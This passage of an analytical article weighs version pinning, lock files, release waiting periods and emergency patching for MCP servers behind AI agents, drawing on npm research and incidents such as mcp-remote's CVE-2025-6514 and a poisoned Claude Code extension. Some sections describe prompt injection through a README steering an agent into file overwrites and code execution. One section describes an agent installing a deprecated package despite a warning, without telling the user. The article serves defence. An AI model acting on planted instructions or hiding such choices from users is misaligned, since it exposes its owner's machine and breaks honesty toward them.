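Pinning came with 27 per cent more known-vulnerable dependencies and 47 per cent more outdated direct ones, while the median number of floating links fell by only 8 per cent. The benefit was small because direct dependencies are a small part of the dependency tree. The median GitHub project had 11 direct dependencies and 150 transitive ones, excluding development-only packages. Automatic updates fell more, by 18 per cent, but He and colleagues' statistical model explained little of the variation in that measure.

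The numbers of outdated and vulnerable packages depend heavily on the assumption that nobody updates anything by hand for a year. He and his colleagues acknowledge this and note that a project could update its pins every 30 days, for example, or at every new release. Their method also pins each dependency to the lowest version that its version range allowed, which may already have been old on the first date. A developer who pinned the current releases and checked them monthly would have fewer outdated and vulnerable packages than the table shows. She would still have most of the floating links, because updating direct dependencies doesn't pin the packages they depend on.

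The comparison may also understate the benefit of pinning for someone who now uses only version ranges, because many of the projects in the column of real settings already pinned some of their dependencies.

### Why pins can add floating links

In npm, pinning direct dependencies can increase the number of floating links. When two parts of a program need the same package, npm looks for one version that satisfies both. If it can't find one, it installs two copies, each with its own dependencies.

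Suppose a mail server for agents uses two packages, `logger` and `mailer`, and `mailer` also needs `logger`. Each version of `logger` needs three small packages and accepts a range of versions of each. The newest `logger` is 1.4.0.

| Link | With ranges | With direct pins |
|---|---|---|
| Server to `logger` | `^1.2.0`, floating | `1.2.0`, fixed |
| Server to `mailer` | floating | fixed |
| `mailer` to `logger` | `^1.3.0`, floating | `^1.3.0`, floating |
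| Copies of `logger` installed | 1.4.0 | 1.2.0 and 1.4.0 |
| Links from `logger` to its three packages | 3 floating | 6 floating |
| Total floating links | 6 | 7 |

With version ranges, the server and `mailer` can share version 1.4.0. The pin to 1.2.0 prevents this, so npm installs a second copy, and the developer gains three dependency links after fixing two.

A larger tree offers more chances for such conflicts. He and colleagues fitted a regression that estimates the effect of pinning from the number of packages in the tree:

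```
change in ln(floating links + 1) = −0.519 + 0.084 × ln(packages)
```

For an npm server with 69 packages, the number in Corelight's case, this gives −0.519 + 0.084 × ln(69), or about −0.16. Since e to the power of −0.16 is about 0.85, pinning every direct dependency would leave the server with some 15 per cent fewer floating links. Other sizes give different results:

| Packages in the tree | Estimated effect of direct pins on floating links |
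|---|---|
| 10 | 28% fewer |
| 69 | 15% fewer |
| 200 | 7% fewer |
| 498 | None |
| 1,000 | 6% more |

He and colleagues place the crossover at 498 packages, and 26 per cent of the GitHub projects in their sample were at least that large. The rounded coefficients printed here give about 482. For a project with 69 packages, the same method estimates the effect on known-vulnerable dependencies as 0.011 + 0.028 × ln(69), or about 0.13. The number of vulnerable dependencies, plus one, would therefore rise by about 14 per cent if nobody updated the pins.

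The 69-package figures are only an illustration, because Corelight's server used Python. Python's installers allow only one version of each package in an environment, so a pin can't create a second copy. He and colleagues expect direct pins outside npm to reduce exposure slightly rather than increase it, but to cause more conflicts that developers have to resolve. The figures also apply to a server's publisher rather than its users, who can't change the dependencies it declares.

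The increase in large trees may matter less than it sounds, because He and colleagues count links, while an attacker takes over packages. If both copies of `logger` in the mail server example use the same three small packages and accept the same versions of them, the seventh link gives an attacker no new way in. The risk grows only if the older copy needs a different package or accepts versions that the newer one doesn't. The study's finding that direct pins leave most of the tree floating is firmer, because it doesn't depend on how one counts duplicates.

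### Locking the whole tree

He and colleagues advise application developers to lock the entire dependency tree and share the lock file with everyone who works on the project. A lock file is stronger than pinning direct dependencies because it covers transitive ones too. In their sample, 44 per cent of the GitHub projects stored an npm lock file. The word "futile" in the paper's title refers to direct pins as a defence against malicious updates, so the study supports Corelight's remedy.

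*How uv.lock Hash Pinning Saved Us from the litellm Supply Chain Attack* (Bob, 2026) describes how attackers published two malicious releases of the Python package `litellm`, 1.82.7 and 1.82.8, on 24 March 2026. The releases stole credentials and contained a file that Python runs whenever it starts, so a program could trigger it without using `litellm`. Bob's project had `litellm` only because another package, `dspy`, needed it. The project's lock file held `litellm` at 1.80.0, so the malicious releases were never installed. Pinning only `dspy` would have allowed any `litellm` version in the range `dspy` declared. This is an informal account of one project, but it shows the protection that Corelight's server lacked.

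Lock files also have drawbacks. He and colleagues write that npm applies a lock file only to the project being run, not to packages that other people install as dependencies, so each developer has to maintain her own. They add that the format makes it hard to update or audit one package at a time. A developer who regenerates the lock file from scratch to get one fix may receive dozens of other changes. The locked code also becomes outdated, and someone has to decide when to replace it.

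Some tools with "lock" in their name cover less than a full lock file. *mcp-lock* records the exact version and package hash of each npm server an agent uses, then checks them at later starts. Its documentation compares it to `npm ci`, which installs a project's complete dependency tree from its lock file. The documentation also cites a March 2026 attack on `axios`, in which projects that accepted `^1.14.0` received the malicious version 1.14.1. But an agent's owner would normally receive `axios`, a library for making web requests, as a dependency of a server. The server's own package would not change, so its hash would still match. In its sample output, the tool also skips a Python server that it cannot lock.

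OpenTelemetry's *Supply-chain security* describes a stricter routine at a project that makes open-source software for monitoring other programs. Contributors install exactly what is in the reviewed lock file. Worms have spread through the scripts that packages can run during installation, and the project blocks these scripts unless a reviewer has approved them. Each approval applies to one exact version, so a malicious patch release does not inherit the previous release's approval. The project also records refusals, so nobody has reviewed a package that has no record.

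This amounts to re-authorisation for dependencies, and a company could apply it to the servers behind its agents. The lock file does not cover one download, though. The project allows a script that downloads Hugo, a program for building websites, and settings on the contributor's machine can redirect that download or remove its version pin. An administrator who allows such a script has to check both the package that contains it and what the script downloads.

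### Reviewing once for everybody

If every agent's owner locked and reviewed 69 packages independently, thousands of people would read the same code, and most would soon stop. For this reason, He and colleagues simulated what would happen if a few well-placed maintainers did this work for all npm users.

They used a map of the npm registry with about 1.6 million packages and 7.9 million dependency links. In their scenario, an attacker takes over one of the 1,000 packages whose compromise would affect the most downloads. Without any defence, an average attack reaches 1.93 per cent of all npm downloads. They then let a small number of packages pin their dependencies and review each update before accepting it. The most effective selection method favoured packages that have many downloads and lie on many dependency paths.

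| Packages that pin and review | Reduction in risk with npm's present rules | Reduction if pins pass downstream |
|---|---|---|
| 20 | 12% | 51% |
| 100 | 30% | 76% |

Under the current rules, a package can pin only its direct dependencies. The last column shows the effect of letting it pass its complete locked tree to everyone who installs it, which would require a change to npm. With 100 defended packages, this would reduce the average attack's reach from about 1.4 per cent of downloads to about 0.5 per cent.

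These estimates are optimistic because the simulated maintainers spot every malicious update and accept every harmless one without delay, and everyone else uses version ranges. He and colleagues also assume that malicious releases stay available for a long time, citing an earlier study's average of 209 days. Review would prevent far less harm from an attack that the registry removes within hours. Reviewers also make mistakes, and an attacker who knew which 100 packages had good reviewers could target a different one. But both columns assume the same perfect review, so the difference between them comes from letting other people inherit the result.

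Docker already does something similar for the MCP servers in its catalogue, which it offers as container images. Each entry for a server that Docker builds must name a Git commit, and an automatic check rejects entries with a missing or malformed commit. Docker chose commits because nobody can put different code behind the same hash, so a review of a commit stays valid. It also records the commit in the image's metadata, so an administrator can trace a running server to the source code that Docker reviewed.

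Moving an entry to a newer commit requires a new review. Two AI coding agents, Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex, read the incoming changes, write a report and label risks, and a person makes the final decision. Docker recognises that an attacker can hide instructions for the reviewing agents in comments or file names. The human decision provides some protection if the person checks more than the agents' report when a change is suspicious.

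This kind of review would have had a good chance of catching the postmark-mcp update, which changed the server's own code. The `litellm` attack would have been much harder to catch, because a server that uses `litellm` can pick up a malicious release without any change to its own code. Docker's reviewers start with the servers that people install, while the packages in He and colleagues' simulation are mostly deeper in the dependency tree, where one review protects many programs, so the two approaches would work well together.

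Pinning the commit doesn't determine which dependencies go into the image either. If the build installs packages from version ranges, two images built from the same commit on different days can contain different code, as in some of the installations Corelight criticised. But an administrator who pins the finished image by its hash gets a complete, fixed set of packages without maintaining a lock file.

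Stacklok, which also distributes MCP servers as containers, rebuilt its images after the npm attack. It advised maintainers to publish new versions even if they believed the attack had not affected them, in case a build during the attack had included a malicious dependency. Users who have pinned an image by its hash won't receive the rebuilt one until they change the hash.

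## Security patches that pinned agents miss

A pinned server keeps its flaws as well as its good behaviour. In the npm projects that He and colleagues studied, neglected pins therefore led to 27 per cent more dependencies with known vulnerabilities. Two flaws that developers fixed in 2025 show how this can affect an agent's owner.

### Commands from a hostile server through mcp-remote

The program mcp-remote lets an agent that supports only local servers use hosted ones. The agent launches it like a local server, and it relays messages to and from the hosted server. JFrog's *Critical RCE Vulnerability in mcp-remote* (2025) describes a flaw, CVE-2025-6514, in versions 0.0.5 to 0.1.15. When a hosted server asks the user to log in, it supplies the address of a login page. The flawed versions opened that address without checking it properly, so a hostile server could instead supply text that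 the user's computer would run as a command.

JFrog, the security company that found the flaw, could use it to run any command on Windows. On macOS and Linux, it could start programs but had limited control over what they did. JFrog rated the flaw 9.6 out of 10, and the maintainer fixed it in version 0.1.16.

A user pinned to mcp-remote 0.1.15 was at risk if she connected to a malicious server or if someone hijacked a server she trusted. An attacker on her local network could also impersonate a server she reached over an unencrypted connection. The risk was much lower if she used only one well-run server over HTTPS. JFrog lists that restriction as an alternative to updating, so she could reduce the risk while she tested 0.1.16. The sample settings in JFrog's report launch mcp-remote without a version number, so anyone who had copied settings like these would have received the fix the next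 time `npx` fetched the latest release.

JFrog calls its demonstration the first full takeover "in a real-world scenario", meaning a realistic set-up, not an attack on an actual victim. The official record, MITRE's *OS command injection in mcp-remote when connecting to untrusted MCP servers* (2025), lists exploitation as "none". A copy at GCVE, another vulnerability database, attributes this assessment to CISA, the US government's cybersecurity agency. CISA made it on 9 July 2025, the day the flaw became public, so it doesn't cover anything attackers did after they could read how the attack worked.

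SD Times lists three more MCP projects that needed fixes that summer, including the MCP Python SDK, which mishandled malformed requests until version 1.9.4. Many Python servers depend on the SDK, so a lock file that pinned an older version could have kept the flaw in a server even if the server's own code needed no fix.

### Six months to repair Anthropic's Git server

Anthropic's Git server lets an agent read and change code repositories. The owner can name one repository when launching the server, but the server did not check that the agent stayed within that repository. Cyata's *How We Found Code Execution in Anthropic’s Official Git MCP Server* describes this flaw and two others. An attacker could exploit all three through prompt injection, planting instructions in text the agent will read, such as a project's README file.

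The planted instructions could make the agent open other repositories, turn any folder into a repository, or overwrite files. If the agent also had a tool for writing files, as many coding agents do, the attacker could run code on the machine. The attacker could also use the flaws to bring private files into the model's context, but would have needed another way to get them out.

Cyata gives this timeline for 2025:

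```
24 June        Cyata sends its first report to Anthropic
25 June        Anthropic classes it as informative
6 July         Cyata reports file overwriting and code execution
24 July        Anthropic reopens the report
10 September   Anthropic accepts it
17 December    Anthropic commits a fix
```

During these 176 days, a user who updated every morning was exposed to the same flaws as one who never updated. Updating quickly helped only once a fix existed. It also matters most then, because a published fix shows attackers what to look for in older copies. TechRadar's *Anthropic's official Git MCP server had some worrying security flaws* reported no evidence of exploitation as of January 2026.

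The first public advice gave the wrong version number. INCIBE's *CVE-2025-68144* (2025), an entry from Spain's national cybersecurity institute, told users on 17 December to install version 2025.12.17 "when it is released". Cyata and The Hacker News (2026) both give 2025.12.18 as the patched version, so an administrator who acted on the first notice had to check again.

According to INCIBE, the fix for one flaw makes the server reject inputs that Git would mistake for command options. A fix like this can leave every tool's name, description and input format unchanged. Without the advisory, someone comparing capability lists would have seen no reason to upgrade, just as Dev saw no reason to refuse the email-copying release of postmark-mcp.

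### Servers that nobody will repair

Some flawed tools have no patched version. Glow Labs, a security research group, studied transcripts of coding sessions in which an AI agent installed or suggested a deprecated MCP server, one that its publisher no longer supports. In 98 per cent of them, the agent appears to have taken the package name from its model's training data, according to Help Net Security. In the rest, the user had asked for the old package. Glow Labs looked only at sessions with a deprecated server, so the 98 per cent figure doesn't measure how often agents choose one.

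In one example, a developer asked an agent for a GitHub server. GitHub maintains its own, but the agent chose an old Anthropic reference server from an archived repository. In another session, the agent looked up a package on npm, received a deprecation notice, and installed the package anyway without telling the user.

Glow Labs found four serious flaws in these reference servers. The worst is in the Puppeteer server, which lets an agent control a web browser. An attacker can use a prompt injection to make the server start any program on the machine instead of the browser. The maintainers replied that they had archived the server in May 2025 and would not fix it. Glow Labs had seen no exploitation as of its November 2026 report.

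For these packages, a floating version and a pin to the last release install the same code, so the owner has to replace the server or remove it. Ordinary warning systems may not alert her, because the flaws have no CVE numbers for a scanner to match against her list of installed software.

npm can't easily withdraw the packages either. It allows removal only for little-used packages: no public package may depend on them, one person must own them, and the past week's downloads must number under 300. The old GitHub server had 185,239 downloads in one week and six owners. Glow Labs counted more than 17.3 million downloads of the deprecated packages since July 2025. That total includes repeated installations and probably automated ones, but it suggests that many people still run them. An administrator can catch most such cases by checking a package's deprecation status before approving it and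 again at each review.

### Eleven hours in Cursor's marketplace

In June 2025, Anthropic's Claude Code extension, which connects the company's coding agent to an editor, had a flaw that let a malicious website connect to the extension and read files on the developer's computer. Anthropic released a fix on 13 June, according to an advisory in GitLab's database, and the extension normally updated itself. Datadog Security Labs' *CVE-2025-52882* (2025) dates the public advisory to 23 June, so most users with automatic updates probably received the fix before attackers could read about the flaw.

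On 29 October 2026, updates to the same extension delivered malware. Cursor's *Security notice* reports that a modified copy was available in the editor's marketplace from about 2:27 am to 1:35 pm Pacific time, a little over 11 hours. Cursor says at most 5,000 users were affected. The copy tried to set up a backdoor through SSH, a standard way to log in to computers remotely. It also sent the attacker details about the machine, including the names of settings that might hold passwords or keys, but not their values, according to Help Net Security's *Claude Code extension poisoned with persistent SSH backdoor* (2026).

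The damage was probably smaller than the attacker intended. Turning on remote login required administrator rights that the extension lacked on most machines, and Cursor had the attacker's server taken offline. The extension still left the attacker's key and some startup scripts behind.

Anthropic had not released the malicious copies. *Cursor traces marketplace breach to stolen Fireworks AI credential* (Rojas, 2026) quotes Cursor's later explanation that the attacker used a stolen credential to place them directly on the cache that served the marketplace. The copies carried Anthropic's genuine extension ID and the version numbers 2.1.312 and 2.1.313. Early reports also implicated Open VSX, a public extension registry that Cursor uses, but Cursor later said the attack had not compromised it.

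Developers who had installed an earlier copy of the extension and turned off automatic updates kept that copy, but a version pin did not necessarily protect new installations. A developer who set up a new Windows or Mac computer that morning and asked for exactly 2.1.312 could have received the malicious copy, because the marketplace served it under that number. A hash taken earlier from Anthropic's own build would have exposed the change, but one recorded that morning from Cursor's marketplace would have matched the malware.

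### How package managers apply a waiting period

A waiting period would have kept many people away from that marketplace copy. The installer ignores any release that has not been public for a set time and chooses an older one that fits. In pnpm, an alternative to npm, the setting counts minutes, so seven days looks like this:

```
minimumReleaseAge: 10080
```

Suppose a project accepts any version of `some-server` from 1.2.0 up to, but not including, 2.0.0:

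| Release | Days since publication | What the installer does |
|---|---|---|
| 1.4.1 | 2 | Ignores it |
| 1.4.0 | 9 | Installs it |
| 1.3.0 | 40 | Passes over it because 1.4.0 is newer |

pnpm applies the rule to transitive dependencies too, such as `litellm` in Bob's project. An administrator can also exempt a package when she needs a fix at once.

The Python tool uv has a related setting, `exclude-newer`, that makes it ignore everything uploaded after a given date. An agent's owner could add it to the command that launches a server:

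```
uvx --exclude-newer 2026-11-01 some-server@1.2.3
```

A cutoff date for package releases would also have stopped most of the drift at Corelight, because each rebuild would use the same set of old releases. It is weaker than a lock file with hashes, and it blocks every later security fix until someone moves the date.

Dependabot, GitHub's updating service, proposes upgrades for a person to accept but doesn't control the installer. Its cooldown setting delays routine proposals but not those that fix a known vulnerability. This exemption is important because it lets a team wait a week before adopting new features without also delaying security fixes.

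The waiting period must also start from the right date. If an installer counts from a version's original publication, a tampered copy of an old version passes immediately. An attacker who controls the marketplace's files, as Cursor's attacker did, might therefore avoid the wait. A waiting period works best with a hash recorded from an earlier, trusted copy, but neither the wait nor the hash can delay a change on a hosted server.

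### How quickly people find malicious releases

The attacks described so far give a small and unrepresentative sample:

| Malicious release | Time before removal or public report | Would a seven-day wait have avoided it? |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Code extension in Cursor | 11 hours | Yes, if the count began when the attacker placed the copy |
| Cyberhaven's browser extension | 25 hours | Yes |
| postmark-mcp 1.0.16 | About 8 days | No, by about a day |

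The 209-day average that He and colleagues cite is much longer. The two kinds of evidence need not conflict, because thousands of users and several security companies watch a popular extension, while a fake package with few downloads can sit unnoticed for months. People also hear more about attacks that are caught quickly. A week's wait is therefore a better defence against the hijacking of well-known software than against an obscure server that was malicious from the start.

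Critics of waiting periods object that somebody has to install a new release before anyone discovers that it is harmful. If everyone waits seven days, the first victims appear on day eight and the delay achieves nothing. SC Media's *Fake Visual Studio Code extension for Cursor led to $500K theft* gives this objection some support. It describes a developer who lost $500,000 after installing a fake Open VSX extension for Solidity, a programming language for cryptocurrency contracts. The listing showed 54,000 downloads, though attackers can inflate such counts.

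Supporters reply that scanners can inspect a release without any user installing it, either by reading the code or by running it on an isolated machine and watching what it does. The same Solidity attack also supports their view. According to Snyk, the VS Code team said Microsoft's marketplace removed the fake extension within seconds of publication. Koi claims similar speed for its product in the postmark-mcp case.

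Scanners miss some malicious extensions, however. In 2025 a researcher found an extension on Microsoft's marketplace with a description stating that it uploaded and encrypted users' files. It was still available about eight hours after he publicised it, according to TechRadar's *Malicious AI-made extension with ransomware capabilities*. In *Flawed extension scanning*, a Cursor user reports that the editor installed a malicious extension despite its checks. Some malware also looks for signs that it is running on a test machine. The Hacker News' *Malicious VSX Extension "SleepyDuck" Uses Ethereum to Keep Its Command Server Alive* (2025) describes such an extension. Its first release was harmless, but the next day's update made it malicious.

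How much the objection matters depends on who is likely to find the malware. Suppose early users would find any malicious release in two days on average. Scanners find obvious malware in two days on average, but need 50 for well-hidden malware. If the chance of discovery stays the same each day, these invented numbers leave the following shares undetected after a week:

| Kind of malware | Everyone installs at once | Everyone waits |
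|---|---|---|
| Obvious | 0.1% | 3% |
| Well hidden | 3% | 87% |

If everyone waits before installing new releases, obvious malware takes longer to discover, but people still avoid almost every attack. The critics are mostly right about hidden malware, where a week's delay mainly postpones the harm. In practice some people always install at once, knowingly or not, so actual results fall between the two columns. An organisation that waits is partly relying on those people to take the risk, unless it also pays for scanning or runs new releases on test machines with no valuable data.

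### The expected loss from a delay of *d* days

A simple model shows how long an owner should wait. Let *L*(*d*) be the expected loss from installing a release *d* days after its publication:

```
L(d) = p × s(d) × H  +  q × d × K  +  R

p      chance that the release is malicious
s(d)   share of malicious releases still undetected after d days
H      loss if the owner installs a malicious release
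q      daily chance that someone exploits the flaw the release repairs
K      loss if that happens
R      cost of reviewing the release
```

The first term falls as the delay grows, because other people find more of the bad releases. The second rises each day the old flaw remains. The review cost is the same whenever the review happens, so it doesn't affect the best delay, but it does affect how many integrations an owner can afford.

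All the numbers that follow are invented. Suppose one release in 10,000 is malicious, either kind of attack costs $1,000,000, and a review costs $50. For a routine release, assume a one-in-a-million daily chance that someone exploits an old flaw, which costs $1 a day on average. For an urgent fix, assume a daily chance of one in 5,000, or $200 a day. The expected losses, including the review, are then:

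| Delay | Malicious releases still undetected | Routine release | Urgent fix |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 100% | $150 | $150 |
| 1 day | 50% | $101 | $300 |
| 3 days | 20% | $73 | $670 |
| 7 days | 8% | $65 | $1,458 |
| 14 days | 5% | $69 | $2,855 |
| 30 days | 3% | $83 | $6,053 |

Seven days is the best of these delays for the routine release, because after that the harm from running ageing code outweighs the benefit of catching a few more malicious releases. The owner should install the urgent fix at once, because the first day of waiting avoids $50 of expected harm from malware but adds $200 from the known flaw. With these numbers, immediate installation is best whenever the flaw costs more than $50 a day.

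Applying the same rule to urgent and routine releases wastes money. If one release in 100 is urgent, waiting seven days to install each one costs about $7,900, and installing each one immediately costs $15,000. Installing the urgent one immediately and waiting seven days for the rest costs about $6,600. If more than about six releases in 100 were urgent, installing everything immediately would cost less than waiting a week for everything.

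The same fix can be urgent for one agent and routine for another. CVE-2025-6514 was an emergency for someone whose agent connected to unfamiliar servers through mcp-remote. For a company that used mcp-remote only to reach its own server over HTTPS, *q* was much smaller, and testing version 0.1.16 for a few days before upgrading would have been reasonable.

In the model, an urgent fix is no more likely to be malicious than any other release. But an attacker who knows that security fixes skip the waiting period has a good reason to call his malware a security fix. If the owner can't confirm where an alleged fix comes from, she might put the chance of malice at one in 500. Installing it immediately then costs $2,050, and waiting three days costs $1,050. So the exemption should depend on an independent advisory that names the version, not on the release's own notes.

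She may also be able to do better than either of these by disconnecting the server while she checks the new release. This removes the danger from the old flaw, but she loses the agent's work in the meantime. If that work is worth $100 a day, disconnecting the server for three days would bring the cost of the doubtful fix down to $750.

### Pinning advice and patching deadlines

Official guidance covers routine patching and re-authorisation in different documents. OWASP, a non-profit that publishes widely used lists of software risks, includes the supply chain in its *Top 10 for Agentic Applications* of December 2025. It recommends pinning prompts, tools and settings by content hash, introducing changes in stages, and keeping a way to disable a compromised tool everywhere at once. This advice is closer to re-authorisation than to routine patching, and mostly concerns what an owner should verify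 before a change takes effect.

Governments have set deadlines for software in general. In 2021, CISA ordered US federal agencies to repair flaws on its list of those that attackers were known to exploit, normally within two weeks for newly listed flaws. The British government's Cyber Essentials scheme requires certified organisations to install fixes for high-severity and critical flaws within 14 days of release. These rules treat the two MCP flaws quite differently:

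| Rule | What starts the clock | mcp-remote and Git server flaws |
|---|---|---|
| CISA's 2021 order | Evidence of exploitation and a place on CISA's list | No deadline while nobody has seen exploitation |
| Cyber Essentials | A fix for a high-severity or critical flaw | 14 days |

Waiting for evidence of exploitation before patching focuses limited effort on real attacks but leaves early victims unprotected. Severity scores allow earlier action, but they are less certain than they look. The Hacker News gives the Git server's argument flaw 8.1 under version 3 of the standard scoring system and 6.4 under version 4. Cyber Essentials uses version 3, so its patching deadline would apply. INCIBE uses version 4 and rates the flaw "medium", so an administrator sorting by that label might have postponed the patch.

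An organisation can delay routine releases for seven days and still meet both 14-day limits. But at $200 a day, an urgent fix installed on day 14 would have met the Cyber Essentials requirement and still cost far more than one installed on the first day.

In its 2022 guide to patch management, the US standards institute NIST distinguishes four situations: routine patches, emergency patches, temporary protection before a patch is in place, and systems that nobody can patch. The abandoned servers that Glow Labs found belong in the last group, where the usual response is to isolate or replace the system. The four situations fit agent integrations well, although none of these government rules was written for agents. After the Cursor incident, the consultancy Thoughtworks similarly recommended pinned versions, a short review window and a fast route for verified security patches.

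### Authorising an emergency upgrade

Whoever pins a version has to notice when a security fix is released, which automatic updates would otherwise do. For a server on one person's laptop, this is the user's job. In a company, each integration needs a named owner and a deputy, so that someone can respond to an urgent advisory when the owner is on holiday. The operator of a hosted service watches for flaws in its own code, but the customer still has to watch for flaws in any local program that connects to the service, such as mcp-remote.

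The owner needs a list of the exact versions in use, including transitive dependencies, and a scanner that checks it against a vulnerability database every day. Lagermann told Help Net Security that the MCP servers he maintains are checked for vulnerabilities every night and updated the next morning if necessary. Government notices are a useful second source. In *Critical Vulnerabilities in Claude Code Could Enable Remote Code Execution*, ThaiCERT urged developers to update the coding agent after Anthropic fixed three flaws, one of which bypassed the user's consent.

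Someone must also reread security notices during an incident, because they can change. Cursor first named only version 2.1.313 and published two file hashes for it. Cursor's *セキュリティに関するお知らせ*, a Japanese edition revised on 30 October, adds version 2.1.312 and lists one of those hashes under it. It omits the other hash and now lists two files for 2.1.313, both with new hashes. An administrator who searched only for the first day's hashes could have missed infected machines, although Cursor's other test, a search for the attacker's SSH key, worked for both versions.

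With the owner and the list in place, an emergency upgrade of mcp-remote from 0.1.15 to 0.1.16 could go like this:

1. The owner confirms that an agent uses an affected version and blocks its connections to untrusted servers.
2. She checks that an independent advisory names 0.1.16, and that the release comes from the usual publisher.
3. She reads the code change, to which the official CVE record links directly, and compares the old and new tool definitions.
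4. A second person, on call for such decisions, approves that exact version and hash and exempts it from the waiting period.
5. The owner tries it on one agent, then installs it everywhere and restores the connections.

The approval should cover only this release. If the company exempted every future version of mcp-remote, an attacker who later took over the package could also skip the waiting period. If the fix also adds tools or requests new OAuth scopes, the owner can leave them switched off and decide on them later through the ordinary review, since the urgency of the fix doesn't justify rushing their approval.

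Step 4 needs a deputy with the authority to decide, or the process will fail the first time a decision is needed at a weekend. It also needs a time limit. If nobody answers within, say, four hours, the safer default for a critical flaw is to disconnect the integration until someone does. That interrupts the agent's work, which gives managers a practical reason to keep the rota filled.

### Going back to an earlier version

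An upgrade can fail even after careful tests, so the owner should first save the old package, its lock file, the approved tool definitions and the client's settings. She can't rely on the publisher to keep old releases. After the June 2025 flaw in the Claude Code extension, for example, the extension stores removed every vulnerable version, according to Datadog Security Labs. To roll back, she restores all four together, since a client that runs old code but still has the new definitions will raise false alarms or send malformed calls. She also revokes any scopes that the new version received.

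Rolling back a security fix restores the flaw. If 0.1.16 had broken an agent's connection, returning to 0.1.15 would have let hostile servers exploit the flaw again. The owner can prevent an accidental rollback by setting a minimum version alongside the pin. If the fixed version doesn't work, she has to keep the integration disconnected or limit it to servers she trusts until the publisher releases another fix.

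A rollback also can't undo what the agent did after the upgrade. It can't unsend messages, and the new version may have converted stored data into a form that the old one can't read. For a tool that changes important records, the owner needs a backup from just before the upgrade.

Reinstalling the previous version is not enough to recover from a malicious release. After the user removed the modified Claude Code extension, its scripts kept running and the attacker's key stayed on the machine. Cursor advises users to isolate affected computers, remove the key and the scripts, consider rebuilding the machine, and replace every credential accessible from it. Replacing the credentials from a different, trusted computer is safer, because an intruder may still be able to read whatever users type on the affected one.
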